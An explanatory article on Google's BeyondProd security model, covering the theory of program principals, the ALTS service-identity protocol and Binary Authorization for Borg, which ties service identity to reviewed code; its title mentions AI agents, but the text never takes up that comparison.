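# Google's BeyondProd: tying a service's trust to reviewed code, and what the equivalent would be for an AI agent

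## Trusting a caller for the program it runs: background and early theory

BeyondProd is the security model that Google uses for its production systems, the data-centre programs behind its products. A program's access depends on its cryptographic identity, whether its code was reviewed, and whether the machine running it passed an integrity check. Its network location does not count, unlike in many older networks, where a program could reach data because it was inside the firewall or at an approved address. Google first published the design in 2019, and its current description dates from May 2024. The idea of trusting a program for its code goes back at least to research of the early 1990s.

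A storage service that holds users' mail receives a network request for Alice's mail. What should the service establish about the caller before it answers?

A *service* is a program that does one job for other programs or for users, such as storing mail or producing the page where Alice reads it. The caller here would normally be the service that produces the page, called the mail frontend. It sends its request as a *remote procedure call* (RPC), which lets one program invoke a function in another across a network. Google packages its services in *containers*, which bundle a program with the files it needs, and its container manager, Borg, deploys several billion containers a week. The frontend may run on one machine at noon and on another an hour later, so its network address is poor evidence of which program is calling.

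Many companies relied on the address anyway. In *BeyondCorp*, Ward and Beyer (2014) compared the usual corporate network to a medieval castle, where everyone inside the wall is trusted. They described how Google was replacing its own network with access based on the credentials of the user and the device, wherever they connect from. The industry calls this approach *zero trust*, though vendors use the term loosely. In Google's interpretation, which Brewer and Venables give in *A unified and proven Zero Trust system with BeyondCorp and BeyondProd*, implicit trust in any single component is a risk, so a system should establish trust by several means and keep verifying it. Google applied this principle to employees with BeyondCorp and to services with BeyondProd.

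The storage service must check who sent the request (*authentication*) and whether that sender may have what it requests (*authorization*). Cryptography helps with both. A *cryptographic hash*, or digest, is a short fingerprint of a file. Changing one byte of the mail frontend's program file changes its fingerprint, and nobody can feasibly build another file with the original fingerprint. A *signature* is a value that only the holder of a private key can produce and anyone with the matching public key can check. A *certificate* is a signed statement, typically that a particular public key belongs to a particular name. The frontend could present a certificate for the name "mail frontend", signed by an authority that the storage service already trusts.

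A certificate like that establishes the program's name but not what the program will do with the mail. An engineer inside the company could secretly change the frontend to copy Alice's messages somewhere else, and the altered program could keep the same name, key and address. This is *insider risk*, the danger from people who have legitimate access, or from attackers who have taken over their accounts. Google gives each service an authenticated name through a protocol called ALTS, and ties the name to reviewed code through a check called Binary Authorization for Borg. The theory explains why the second step is needed, and what it can and cannot establish.

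### Programs as holders of permissions

Permission lists traditionally name people. Lampson, Abadi and colleagues at Digital Equipment Corporation added programs in *Authentication in Distributed Systems* (1992). Their theory covers *principals*, meaning anything that can be the source of a statement: a person, a machine, an encryption key, or a program running on a machine.

The theory relies mainly on two relations. "A says s" means that we may proceed as though principal A had made the statement s. "A speaks for B", written A ⇒ B, means that whenever A says something, we may take B to have said it too. For example, a key speaks for the person who holds it. The paper's handoff rule, which every certificate in the system uses, establishes new "speaks for" relations: if A′ already speaks for A, and A′ says that B speaks for A, then B does speak for A.

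An operator called "as" combines a machine and the program it runs into one principal. A machine N running a program with digest D is the principal "N as D". The statement "N as D says s" is defined as "N says (D says s)", which means the machine is quoting the program it loaded.

Now the mail request. Let K be the machine's public key, P the name "mail frontend", and r the request "read Alice's mail". The access list on the mail contains the entry "N as P". The storage service begins by trusting one certification authority, CA, to speak for the names N and P. It then has three things in hand:

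1. CA says K ⇒ N
2. CA says D ⇒ P
3. K says (D says r)

The handoff rule gives K ⇒ N from line 1 and D ⇒ P from line 2. Because K speaks for N, line 3 becomes N says (D says r), which is (N as D) says r. Because D speaks for P, (N as D) speaks for (N as P), so (N as P) says r. That principal is on the access list, so the storage service hands over the mail.

Line 3 is where the machine vouches for the program. N computed the digest itself, before starting the program, and nothing in the derivation checks that it did so honestly. Lampson and colleagues are plain about this: anyone who trusts a machine to run P has to trust it not to lie about running P. (For the same reason N can check line 2 on its own and simply report the name P, and the storage service need never see the digest.)

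The paper bases trust in a machine on its hardware. Each machine holds a private key in permanent memory. When it restarts, its boot code identifies the operating system by its digest, creates a new key pair, gives the private key to the operating system, and signs a certificate that the new key speaks for this machine running that system. The hardware then hides the machine's own key until the next restart. Otherwise, one operating system could impersonate any other that the machine would load, and a single compromised system would compromise the machine permanently.

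Line 2 is easier to overlook but matters more here. In this theory, a program is anything that obeys a given specification, so successive versions of the mail frontend can share the name P, each with its own digest and certificate. But the logic takes the certificate as a premise, so someone has to decide that a given file should have the name P, and the theory includes no method for making that decision.

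The paper offers two ways to use the decision, with virus control as the worked example. A machine can load any program but give uncertified ones the identity "unknown", which appears on few access lists. Or it can refuse to load uncertified programs, which suits machines that cannot protect themselves from a running program. The paper's example of such a machine is a PC running MS-DOS.

The theory also covers delegation. The frontend should receive Alice's mail only when it is acting for her, and the paper writes a principal B acting on A's behalf as "B for A". Both parties must consent, and A's delegation expires after perhaps 30 minutes unless A renews it. A frontend that nobody is using would then have no authority over anybody's mail. The group built all this into a working operating system, Taos. *Authentication in the Taos Operating System* (Wobber, Abadi and colleagues, 1994) reports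 that the system was efficient enough for a substantial number of users.

### Remote attestation, and what a hash leaves out

Within one company, an administrator can install a key in each machine and vouch for that machine. This is harder between strangers, and in the early 2000s the computer industry proposed a standard chip for this purpose, the Trusted Platform Module (TPM). In the resulting procedure, called *remote attestation*, a machine sends another party a hardware-signed report of the software it has loaded.

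In *Property-based Attestation for Computing Platforms* (2004), Sadeghi and Stüble describe how a computer uses a security chip called a TPM to attest to the software it runs. At startup, a small trusted component hashes the firmware and the first code on the boot disk, and writes the result into protected registers on the chip. The boot code then hashes whatever it loads next, and so on up to the operating system. The chip signs the register contents when a remote party asks for them. To cover an application as well, the operating system signs a hash of its program file. The remote party checks the whole chain and compares each hash with a list of software it approves. The two sides must also establish a shared secret. Otherwise, as Haldar, Chandra and Franz point out in *Semantic Remote Attestation* (2004), an attacker could attest with an approved program and then communicate using a different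 one.

Both papers appeared in 2004, and both question the value of the signed hash. Their first objection is that any patch changes the hash, so the list of approved software is always going out of date. Users also apply different combinations of patches, and ten optional patches allow 1,024 versions of one program. The TPM can also *seal* data, releasing it only to a machine whose measured software matches a stated configuration, so a routine security patch can lock owners out of their own files. Sadeghi and Stüble add that a content provider that cannot examine every configuration will approve only a few mainstream ones, which may shut out Linux users.

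The other, more basic complaint is that the remote party wants assurance about behaviour, and a hash only identifies a file. The hash will still match if the file has bugs or if its vendor wrote it to misbehave. The measurement also happens only once, at launch, so a program whose behaviour depends on data it reads later can do very different things under the same hash.

The update problem is less serious when one operator controls every version of the software. Haldar and colleagues concede that approved lists are workable for closed systems of this kind, such as cash machines. A company that builds its own software and runs it in its own data centres is in much the same position, since it can keep a record of every build. But even for such a company, knowing exactly which file is running helps only if somebody knows what that file does.

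Sadeghi and Stüble proposed attesting a machine's properties instead of its configuration, because the remote party usually cares about a property, such as strict isolation between processes, rather than which operating system provides it. In their scheme, a trusted third party examines a configuration and signs a certificate stating that it has the property. In one variant, the machine proves that it holds a valid certificate for its current software without revealing what that software is. Updates become easier because a patched system needs only a new certificate for the same property before keys bound to the old version can move to the new one.

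This deals well with updates and vendor lock-out, but less well with behaviour. Like line 2 of the derivation, the property certificate is a signed claim that a given digest deserves a given label, and someone still has to find out whether the claim is true. According to the paper, determining the properties of a real configuration is "difficult, if not impossible". A new bug can also make a certificate false after the third party has signed it. Short-lived certificates are a simple remedy, but the paper describes them as unsatisfying and sketches others, such as a list of certified configurations from which the third party can remove the insecure ones.

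Haldar and colleagues proposed checking a program's behaviour directly by running it inside a trusted virtual machine, a layer of software that executes another program's code and can therefore inspect it beforehand and monitor it as it runs. The remote party asks the virtual machine to check a specific rule. Their prototype, a modified Java virtual machine, ran a simple file-sharing protocol in which dishonest participants could flood a victim with traffic by sending false messages. The remote server supplied a small program that examined each outgoing message, checking that announcements carried the sender's true address and that files on offer existed. A run of 5,000 exchanges between two machines took between 9.5 and 10.2 seconds with or without the checks.

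A second prototype applied testing to a project that searches for large prime numbers by sending work to volunteers' computers, whose arithmetic varies in speed and accuracy. The server sent a test suite for the virtual machine to run, and used the signed results to decide which work each computer should get.

These checks test behaviour, so a patched program passes them as long as it still follows the rules, but they are narrow. A rule such as "does nothing improper with Alice's mail" is harder to state than two properties of a message format, and according to the paper, few existing analyses covered the high-level rules that would be useful to a remote server. Hashes are also still needed, because the remote party has to trust the virtual machine and its libraries, and it identifies those by their hashes.

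### Pedigree, analysis and encapsulation

By 2011 there were several different reasons for trusting a program. *Nexus Authorization Logic (NAL)* (Schneider, Walsh and Sirer, 2011) brought them into one logic, an extension of "says" and "speaks for". A decision to grant access in NAL can rest on the requester's source or *pedigree*, on the outcome of a mechanical *analysis* of the requester, or on trusted software that *encapsulates* or modifies the requester. *Logical Attestation* (Sirer, de Bruijn and colleagues, 2011), the companion paper on the Nexus operating system, calls these grounds axiomatic, analytic and synthetic, respectively.

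A vendor's signature on a software package and a match against a list of approved hashes are both forms of pedigree, because the user accepts the program based on who stands behind it. A typechecker is a form of analysis that examines code before it runs and rejects whole classes of error. A sandbox is a form of encapsulation that lets a program run but blocks it from most of the machine. Real systems combine these approaches. Java, for example, checks types before a program runs and adds further checks while it runs.

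Sirer and colleagues give an example in which different grounds for trust can substitute for one another. A program may read a sensitive file only if it cannot leak the contents to the disk or the network. One acceptable credential is a statement from a named company that the program, identified by its hash, is trustworthy. Another, which does not depend on who wrote the program, comes from an analyser that traces the communication channels between running processes and finds no path from the program to the disk or the network. When analysis cannot settle a question in advance, Nexus can place a monitor between a process and everything it communicates with, to inspect, alter or block each message. In tests on a web server, such monitors cut throughput by about half in the worst case, but by only 6% once the system reused earlier decisions.

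Each ground for trust has its own limits. Pedigree is only as reliable as the judgement of whoever signed. Analysis covers only the properties that someone has managed to define and check automatically. Encapsulation stops only what a monitor can recognize as forbidden. A monitor around the mail frontend can block a connection to an unknown server, but it will have difficulty detecting a frontend that shows Alice's mail to Bob, because showing mail to users is the frontend's job.

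Google relies heavily on pedigree for code that its own engineers write. Reviewers examine the code, but at deployment the system verifies a signed record that the program went through the required process. Where pedigree is weaker, as with code from outside the company, Google adds encapsulation by running the program under stronger isolation, such as gVisor, a layer that intercepts the program's calls to the operating system.

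## ALTS: an identity for every service, from 2007

Google began work on authenticated names for its services in 2007. Its protocol, Application Layer Transport Security (ALTS), lets two services prove their identities to each other and protects the data they exchange. *Application Layer Transport Security* (Ghali, Stubblefield and colleagues, 2017) describes the design as of December 2017. Google has since changed parts of the protocol, mainly the cryptography.

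The obvious alternative was TLS (Transport Layer Security), which protects most web traffic. But in 2007 TLS came with support for old protocols that fell below Google's minimum security standards. Google could have kept the good components and written the rest itself, but its engineers decided that a new system had more advantages. Google controlled both ends of every connection, so ALTS did not need to work with older versions of anything. A small protocol is also easier to inspect by hand and to *fuzz*, which means feeding it large amounts of malformed input to find bugs. ALTS could also use Protocol Buffers, the data format in which most Google services already exchanged messages. Ghali and colleagues compare its security only with the TLS of that period, claiming that ALTS was historically more secure than "older TLS".

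By 2017 Google's production services were issuing on the order of ten billion RPCs per second, and ALTS protected them by default, without developers having to configure anything. Google (2017) announced the paper with the example of the Gmail frontend calling a storage backend, the mail request from the previous section.

### Names that do not depend on machines

On the web, a TLS certificate ties a server to a specific name, such as a web address, under a specific naming scheme. An ALTS certificate contains an identity that works with several naming schemes and does not depend on where the program runs. Borg can therefore start more copies of the mail frontend, spread requests among them, or move one to another machine, and every copy authenticates as the mail frontend. Two different jobs on one machine each authenticate under their own identity.

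People and machines have ALTS identities too. For services, Ghali and colleagues give the example of a product with a frontend and a backend. Site reliability engineers, the staff who keep production systems running, can launch `service-frontend-prod` and `service-backend-prod`. Developers can build and launch test versions, `service-frontend-dev` and `service-backend-dev`. The production services' access rules exclude the development identities, so the production backend refuses requests from a half-finished frontend even if its certificate is valid.

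This arrangement limits who can run code under a production name. But developers manage some production services directly, and the person who writes the code for those services may also launch it.

### How a job gets its certificate

ALTS certificates form a chain with three links. The first is Google's *Signing Service*'s public verification key, and every Google machine in the data centres and on the corporate network has a copy. The Signing Service signs *master certificates*, each containing a public key for an identity. Whoever holds the matching private key can sign *handshake certificates*, which services present to each other when they connect.

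A handshake certificate includes the master certificate above it, so the recipient can follow the signatures back to the key already on its machine. Google replaces handshake certificates often, and signing them with the master certificate's key means the Signing Service doesn't have to sign each one.

For jobs, the Borg controller creates the handshake certificates. One controller manages each Borg cluster, which Google calls a cell. The process has five steps:

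1. The controller starts with a master certificate for its own machine and the matching private key.
2. A background program uses that key to sign a handshake certificate for the controller, which can now make ALTS calls itself.
3. The controller creates a new key pair for certifying jobs and asks the Signing Service to sign a master certificate for it. The signed certificate names the controller as its issuer.
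4. A client asks the controller to run a job under a particular identity. The controller checks that this client may run jobs as that identity. If so, it assigns the job to a machine, issues a handshake certificate and private key, and sends both over an ALTS connection to the Borg agent on that machine.
5. The job uses the certificate whenever it makes an ALTS call.

The first three steps prepare the controller, and the last two happen for each job. The controller issues the private keys as well as the certificates, so an attacker who took it over could impersonate the jobs in its cluster.

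Step 4 matters most for the question of trusted code. The controller checks the permissions of the person or system launching the job but, as the step is described, doesn't check the contents of the program. In the 1992 theory by Lampson and colleagues, the storage service relied on the statement D ⇒ P, meaning that a program with digest D speaks for the name P, "mail frontend". In ALTS, the controller instead certifies that a *key* speaks for P, because an authorized client asked it to. Strictly, the certificate means that someone with permission to launch mail frontends launched this job.

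### Checking the issuer

The Signing Service signs the request and records who made it, but does not decide who should get which identity. Another service makes that decision later, when it receives the certificate and checks it against the *ALTS policy*. This document, copied to every production machine, lists which issuers may issue which categories of certificate for which identities. It allows Google's internal certificate authority to issue certificates to people and machines, and the Borg controller to issue them to jobs.

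Ghali and colleagues illustrate this with Mallory, an employee who wants to act as Network Admin, an identity that can reconfigure the network. Mallory requests a master certificate for Network Admin, and the Signing Service signs it, listing Mallory as the issuer. She then uses her private key to sign a handshake certificate. Both signatures are genuine, but when she tries to connect to another service as Network Admin, that service checks the policy, which does not allow Mallory to issue a master certificate for Network Admin, and the handshake fails.

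In the language of the 1992 theory, the signature on Mallory's certificate establishes only that *Mallory says* her key speaks for Network Admin. That is true, and it is harmless as long as nobody accepts her claim without checking it. Google checks at this later point so that a test cluster can apply a more permissive policy than a production cluster to the same certificates. The drawback is that security now depends on every receiving machine having the right policy.

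### Replacing and revoking certificates

How long a certificate lasts depends on its holder. An employee who authenticates with a password and a second factor gets a handshake certificate valid for 20 hours. A production machine gets a new master certificate every few months and new handshake certificates every few hours. It can use the master certificate only while running verified software. The Borg controller replaces its own master certificate about every two days and reissues the handshake certificates of all jobs running in the cluster.

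Many certificates for production machines have no expiry date. A machine with a wrong clock could reject a valid certificate as expired, and Ghali and colleagues report that relying on dates can cause outages. Google instead cancels a certificate by adding the 64-bit number it contains to a *revocation list*. Eight bits of the number give the certificate's category, and the other 56 identify it within that category. A central service allots ranges of these numbers to the certificate authority and to each Borg controller.

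Each machine keeps its own copy of the list and checks it during every handshake. The underlying database is several hundred megabytes, but compression reduces the file sent to machines to a few megabytes. A machine that has not yet received the latest file will still accept a newly cancelled certificate.

Google was still testing this system's deployment in December 2017, according to Ghali and colleagues. Google Cloud's *Application Layer Transport Security* (2017), the web edition of their paper, omits that remark, presumably because the tests had ended by the time Google edited it.

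### The handshake

When the mail frontend connects to the storage service, each has to prove its identity, and the two need a shared secret that nobody else on the network can learn. ALTS does both with a *Diffie-Hellman exchange*. Let G be a publicly known point on an elliptic curve. The frontend has a private number f, and its handshake certificate contains the public value fG. The storage service has a private number s and a certificate containing sG. The frontend multiplies sG by f, the storage service multiplies fG by s, and both get the same value, fsG. An eavesdropper who sees only fG and sG cannot feasibly compute fsG.

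The exchange takes four messages, with the frontend as client and the storage service as server:

1. **ClientInit.** The frontend sends its handshake certificate and a list of the encryption methods it supports.
2. **ServerInit.** The storage service verifies the certificate, chooses from the list and computes fsG. It sends back its own certificate and its choices.
3. **ServerFinished.** The storage service sends a short code, the *authenticator*, as proof that it computed the shared value.
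4. **ClientFinished.** The frontend verifies the storage service's certificate, computes fsG, checks the authenticator and replies with one of its own.

Each side feeds fsG and a transcript of the messages into a key derivation function and gets three secrets. M protects the data that follows, R lets the two sides resume the session later, and A is the key for the authenticators. Each authenticator is a keyed hash of a fixed string, with a different string for each direction. Only someone who knows f or s can compute A, so a thief who copies the frontend's certificate without its private key cannot complete the handshake. If an attacker alters a message on the way, for example to remove the stronger encryption methods from the list, the two transcripts will differ and the authenticators will not match.

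The server sends its two messages together, so the client can start sending encrypted data after one round trip. Bruno Blanchet formally verified the handshake with ProVerif, a tool for checking cryptographic protocols. Martín Abadi, who co-wrote the 1992 theory, helped him.

A separate *record protocol* then uses M to protect the traffic. It divides messages into frames of up to about a megabyte, and both sides count the requests and responses, so a repeated or out-of-order message fails the integrity check. In 2017 ALTS always protected traffic against alteration. It also encrypted all traffic between Google sites, but within a single site it encrypted the contents only if the services were configured for it.

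### Resuming a session

Diffie-Hellman calculations use a lot of computing power at this scale. Google reduces the load by keeping connections open for a long time and letting services resume old sessions with operations that need much less computation.

After the frontend finishes a handshake with one copy of the storage service, that copy gives it a *resumption ticket*, which contains the secret R and the frontend's identity, encrypted with a key the frontend does not have. To reconnect, the frontend sends the ticket back. The server decrypts it and recovers R, which the frontend also knows. Both sides use R to derive new secrets M′, R′ and A′. R′ goes into the next ticket, and ALTS never uses the same R twice.

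A load balancer spreads requests across the copies of a service, so the frontend's next request may go to a copy it has never contacted. The Borg controller therefore gives the same *resumption key* to every job that runs under one identity in one cluster. Any copy of the storage service there can then open a ticket that another copy issued.

The frontend can also give the storage service a ticket containing R and the storage service's identity, encrypted with the resumption key that all the frontends share. If a different frontend connects later, the storage service can send it the ticket. The new frontend can then decrypt the ticket and resume the session that the first frontend established.

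### Known weaknesses

Sharing keys like this has a drawback, which Ghali and colleagues openly accept. Anyone who steals a service's private key can impersonate that service, but in ALTS the thief can also impersonate other services to the victim. This weakness is called *key compromise impersonation*.

This is because an attacker who has stolen the storage service's private number s can take the frontend's public value fG from its certificate and compute fsG without knowing f. The attacker can then derive A, produce a valid ClientFinished message and connect to the storage service as the mail frontend. A stolen resumption key also lets the attacker forge a ticket with any identity. All copies of a service in a cluster share that key, so stealing it from one exposes the others. A variant of the handshake prevents these attacks, but according to Ghali and colleagues it is worth using only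 where resumption isn't wanted.

ALTS also does not encrypt the handshake messages, so an observer on the network can see which services are communicating, but not the data they exchange.

In 2017, ALTS did not provide *forward secrecy* by default. Forward secrecy means using a fresh key pair for each session and then discarding it, so that someone who later steals a long-term key cannot decrypt recorded traffic. The standard ALTS handshake instead used the fixed values in the certificates. Google replaced these often, so a stolen key would expose only the traffic from that key's lifetime, which was about two days for a job. Services could turn on full forward secrecy, which also covered resumed sessions, unlike in TLS 1.2 and earlier.

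TLS 1.3 lets a client resume a session and send data without waiting for a round trip, but with weaker security. Google left this popular optimization out of ALTS, whose connections last so long that Google saw little benefit in opening them faster.

### Changes since 2017

Google Cloud's *Encryption in transit*, updated in April 2025, describes a protocol that now encrypts all traffic by default, both within and between sites. On machines with a suitable network card, the card does the encryption.

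The larger change is to the key exchange. A powerful enough quantum computer could work out f from fG, so an attacker could record traffic today and decrypt it once such a computer exists. Kölbl, Misoczki and Schmieg explain in *Securing tomorrow today* that Google added a second key exchange, NTRU-HRSS, which it expects to resist quantum computers. Google kept the elliptic-curve exchange alongside it, so that an attacker has to break both, because several of the newer candidates had already been broken without a quantum computer. Google could act before official standards existed because it controls every machine that uses ALTS and can switch algorithms again later.

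The handshake keeps the same four messages. *Post-Quantum Cryptography at Google* (Schmieg, 2023) shows the client adding a temporary public key to ClientInit. The server returns, in ServerInit, a ciphertext from which only the client can recover a further secret. Resumed sessions also include this step. Schmieg describes the temporary key as only "somewhat ephemeral", which suggests that clients reuse it for a while. Even so, forward secrecy should be better than in 2017, because the fixed keys alone no longer decrypt recorded traffic.

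Google appears to have started deploying post-quantum cryptography for its internal communications in 2022 and finished later. Google (2024) states that it has protected them this way since 2022, but in July 2023 Schmieg described the rollout to all jobs as only nearly complete, after three years of work and many unforeseen obstacles. *PQC in plaintext* (Porter and Peters, 2025) reports that Google had moved the key exchanges for its internal traffic to ML-KEM, by then an official US standard. Infosecurity Magazine's article on Google's August 2026 roadmap, *Google Cloud Targets 2027 for First Major Post-Quantum Security Milestone*, gives 2025 as the year of completion.

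All this protects the secrecy of traffic, not the certificates. Kölbl and colleagues kept the older signatures because someone who learns to forge one in the future cannot interfere with a session that has already ended. Secrecy was more urgent because attackers can already collect traffic to decrypt later. Once a quantum computer could forge signatures, service identity would also be at risk. According to Ivezic (2026), in *Google Cloud Put Dates on Its PQC Migration*, the same roadmap schedules quantum-resistant authentication for ALTS for 2026 or 2027.

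### A valid identity on altered code

Stronger signatures will not stop the insider from the previous section, who altered the mail frontend. If that engineer is allowed to launch jobs as the mail frontend, the Borg controller issues the altered version a certificate, the handshake succeeds, and the storage service sends the mail.

Every check in this sequence gave the right answer, because the caller does hold the mail frontend's identity. Limiting launch rights to site reliability engineers reduces the number of people who could do this deliberately. It offers less protection against a developer who hides the change in the code, since the engineer who launches the job may not know it is there. To catch either case, the controller would have to check the program as well as the client before issuing the certificate. Google began building that check in 2013.

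## Binary Authorization for Borg: reviewed code as the condition for an identity, from 2013

Google's Binary Authorization for Borg (BAB) makes a service identity depend on the program as well as on the person launching it. Borg will start a job as the mail frontend only if the job's code and configuration meet a policy for that identity. This applies even to people who have permission to launch the mail frontend.

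Google built BAB mainly to reduce insider risk, but honest mistakes can do similar damage. Google's *Deploy only what you trust*, which introduced a version of the check for cloud customers, gives examples of a developer who accidentally deploys a test program to production and someone in a hurry who skips the tests.

Google had dealt with at least one serious insider case by then. *Google fires engineer for violating privacy policies* (2010) reports that the company dismissed an engineer whom the website Gawker accused of accessing four teenagers' accounts without their consent. Google gave no details, so it is unclear whether a check on deployed code would have helped. Engineers can also reach data through administrative tools, which need separate controls.

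The 2013 starting date comes from Google's own later statements. SLSA's *Safeguarding artifact integrity across any software supply chain*, the archived front page of an open standard based on BAB, dates BAB's first internal use to that year, and Google (2023) said in April 2023 that it had used BAB for ten years. Outsiders learned about the system gradually. InfoQ (2017) reported in January 2017 that Google could restrict a service to specific source code that engineers had reviewed, tested and approved. Google published a paper on BAB in December 2019 and last revised it in May 2024.

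### From a code change to a running job

Before a change to the mail frontend can affect anyone's mail, it goes through code review, a verifiable build, deployment in a container, and the assignment of a service identity.

Most of Google's source code is in one central repository, which lets Google enforce its review rule in one place. At least one engineer other than the author must approve each change, and the approvers must include the owners of the affected system. In *Deploying Code*, a chapter of Google's 2020 book *Building Secure and Reliable Systems*, Spradlin, Lodato and colleagues treat review as a form of *multi-party authorization*, in which nobody can make a change alone. They warn that review becomes rubber-stamping unless the reviewer understands the change or asks the author about it.

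The reviewer reads source code, but a machine runs a *binary*, the file that a build system produces from the source. Working out what a binary does by examining it is slow and expensive, so Google needs a reliable record of which source it came from. This is the job of *provenance*. Google's build system runs in an isolated environment that the engineers requesting builds cannot alter. For every build it signs a record of the sources and dependencies, the hashes of the resulting files, and the full build parameters. Spradlin and colleagues recommend these fields for such a record:

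| Field | Contents |
|---|---|
| Authenticity (required) | Usually a signature, showing which system made the record |
| Outputs (required) | A hash of each file that the build produced |
| Sources | The main source code and its exact version |
| Dependencies | Libraries, compilers and other tools that the build used |
| Command | The command that started the build |
| Environment | Anything else needed to repeat the build, such as the processor type |
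| Input metadata | Facts that a later check may need, such as the date of the source code |
| Debugging information | Details with no security role, such as which machine ran the build |
| Versioning | The build time and the version of the record's format |

The record should include the build command and other parameters because they can change the program. For example, the GCC compiler's `-D` option can replace names throughout the source code as it compiles, so an engineer could completely change a program's behaviour without editing the reviewed source. If the person starting a build can choose such options, a later step has to check them.

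The provenance record is also reliable only if the system that signs it is secure. Builds run commands that engineers supply, and a malicious command could steal the signing key or put false information in the record. Spradlin and colleagues recommend that a trusted program prepare the build and sign the record at the end, while the engineer's commands run in a separate environment without access to the key. They also recommend *hermetic* builds, which declare every input in advance and let only the trusted program fetch them. A hidden library or altered compiler is then much less likely to enter the build unrecorded.

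Google trusts its central build service, which needs to build each program only once. Someone who didn't trust the service could repeat the build and compare the two files bit by bit, but builds often take minutes or hours, and a deployment decision may need to happen within milliseconds. Debian, a version of Linux that volunteers maintain, has several parties rebuild its packages independently and publish their results.

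Next, the build system packages the binary in a container image. To deploy it, an engineer submits a *job configuration*, which specifies the image and the program's startup settings. The job then runs under a service identity, and the limits on who may launch it still apply.

### The policy attached to an identity

When a team puts a service on Borg, it writes a *service-specific policy* that defines what code and configuration may run under the service's identity. Google attaches the policy to the identity because one program can run in several places with access to different data. A copy of the mail frontend that developers test on made-up messages needs fewer controls than the copy that handles real users' mail. A policy change is a code change, so a second engineer has to review it.

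By default, a policy has three requirements:

- **The code must be auditable.** Provenance must connect the container image to source code that people can read. Google keeps that source for at least 18 months, even if its author never submits it to the main repository.
- **The code must be submitted.** The build must use source from a specified location in the repository.
- **The configuration must be submitted.** Settings supplied at deployment go through the same review and submission process as code.

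The first two requirements differ when an engineer builds from an unsubmitted draft. The code is auditable because its provenance correctly identifies the draft, which investigators can read later. But it does not meet the second requirement, because it was never submitted to the repository. Google says only that submission "generally implies" that somebody reviewed the code. The policy checks where the code came from and relies on the repository's rules to require the review.

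With provenance, the build system can sign everything with one key and record where the source came from, and each service's policy can name the repository it accepts. Spradlin and colleagues explain that a simpler design, in which the build system signs every acceptable file and deployment checks only the signature, becomes awkward with many services. If each service may run only code from its own repository, the build system needs a separate key for each repository and has to choose the right one every time, and it is hard to confirm that the system is set up to do so.

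The policy check must confirm that the provenance has a valid signature, that the hash in it matches the file awaiting deployment, and that its contents satisfy the policy's rules. Comparing the hashes stops an attacker from presenting a good program's provenance with a bad program. Other rules could require passed tests, a recent scan for known vulnerabilities, or a sufficiently new build, so that nobody can redeploy an old version with a known flaw.

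Google originally stored provenance in a database and looked up each file by its hash. This caused trouble because different builds can produce identical files, and millions of builds had produced an empty file. To approve an empty file, the policy engine had to search their records for one that met the policy. The search took several orders of magnitude longer than the 100-millisecond target, and if it failed, it could produce only an error message such as "None of these 497,129 records met the policy." Spradlin and colleagues now advise sending the provenance along with the file.

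Google also advises applying exactly one policy to each deployment, so that there is no question whether a job must satisfy both of two overlapping policies or only one. A company-wide rule can instead be enforced by checking the individual policies against it. Google abandoned an early policy language because, although flexible, it could not give engineers useful explanations of why a deployment failed. The replacement was much more limited but had better error messages.

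### Why a command-line flag counts as code

The third requirement matters because a setting can change what a program does, even though it is usually much shorter than the program. *Cluster management at Google* (Wilkes, 2015) includes a sample Borg job file that gives the location of a binary and, on the next line, the arguments for starting it. The example sets only a network port, but other arguments, or *flags*, can turn on features, select a database, or set where output goes.

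Suppose the mail frontend has a flag called `--copy_mail_to`, which developers use to send test messages to a debugging server. Reviewers approved it for that purpose, and production jobs leave it empty. Anyone who could set it at launch could send users' mail to a machine of their choice without changing the reviewed binary, its hash or its valid provenance.

This is a version of the objection that researchers raised to remote attestation in 2004, that a program's hash is little guide to its behaviour if that behaviour depends on what the program reads later. BAB partly addresses this by including the settings supplied at deployment in the review, but it does not cover the data the program receives while running.

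Spradlin and colleagues give a more ordinary example, a setting that determines which backend a frontend uses. Pointing the production frontend at a test backend would be a major security and reliability problem. They observe that engineers who know not to build a production program from a private copy of the source may change its configuration without hesitating.

At Google's scale, configuration had become a form of programming. Verma, Pedrosa and colleagues (2015), in *Large-scale cluster management at Google with Borg*, reported tens of millions of lines of it, with tens of thousands of files longer than 1,000 lines. The configuration language includes functions, so a file can calculate a job's settings.

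### The check before the certificate

BAB adds a check before a job starts. When a client requests to run a job as the mail frontend, the Borg controller still checks that the client may do so, then checks with BAB that the job meets the mail frontend's policy. The controller starts the job and issues its ALTS certificate only if the job meets that policy, regardless of how senior the requester is.

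In the notation of the 1992 theory, let P be the name "mail frontend" and K the job's key. Before BAB, the controller certified that K ⇒ P, meaning that K speaks for P, if this condition was true:

client may launch P

Now let D be the program's digest and C its configuration. With BAB the condition becomes:

client may launch P, and (D, C) satisfies the policy for P

The storage service needs no information about D or C. It checks the same kind of certificate as before and relies on the controller to have applied the policy. The theory left open who decides that a particular file deserves a particular name. In Google's system, the service's owners set the conditions in advance, and the review and build records show whether a file meets them.

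In its 2019 announcement, Google described this as a move from *job identity* to *code identity*. Trusting the mail frontend now means trusting specific reviewed code, which nobody can change without approval, instead of everyone who may launch a job under its name. People still matter because they write and review the code.

The check works only at a point that every launch must pass through, which Spradlin and colleagues call a *choke point*. Their example is Kubernetes, the open-source container manager that Google created. Its worker machines should accept jobs only from the central controller, because otherwise an attacker could bypass the policy by sending a job straight to a worker. The software beneath the containers, such as the operating system, reaches a machine by a different route and needs its own check.

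Software that runs on other people's computers has no such controller, so Google checks it earlier. For the Chrome browser, for example, the build system records each build's sources, parameters and output hashes, and a policy engine examines this provenance before Google signs a release (Mukherjee, 2021, *The Chromium Chronicle #23*).

### Daily checks, emergencies and exceptions

A job's policy can change while the job is running, so BAB checks jobs against the latest version of their policies at least once a day. If it finds a violation, it notifies the service's owners. Google does not describe BAB stopping the job by itself. Automatically shutting down a mail service, for example, could do more harm than the violation.

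Spradlin and colleagues report that the launch request alone did not contain enough information to judge a Borg job afterwards, so Google had to combine three sets of logs, covering jobs, software packages and reserved machine resources.

Sometimes Google has to run code before anyone can review it. If the mail service is down, for example, waiting for the normal process could prolong the outage. BAB could also fail and block a legitimate deployment. In either case, a developer can set an emergency flag and launch the job without passing the policy check.

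The developer must give a justification. BAB logs it with details of the job and a reference to a snapshot of the deployed code, then notifies Google's central security team and the team that owns the identity. The daily check also looks for jobs launched this way. These measures make misuse easier to detect, but an attacker may have copied some mail before anyone responds. Spradlin and colleagues add that emergency launches have to be rare, because investigators cannot pick out a malicious one among many legitimate ones.

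For its most critical services, such as those that manage identity and access, Google requires a second employee's approval even in an emergency. It makes an exception in case its staff lock themselves out of the systems they need to restore access.

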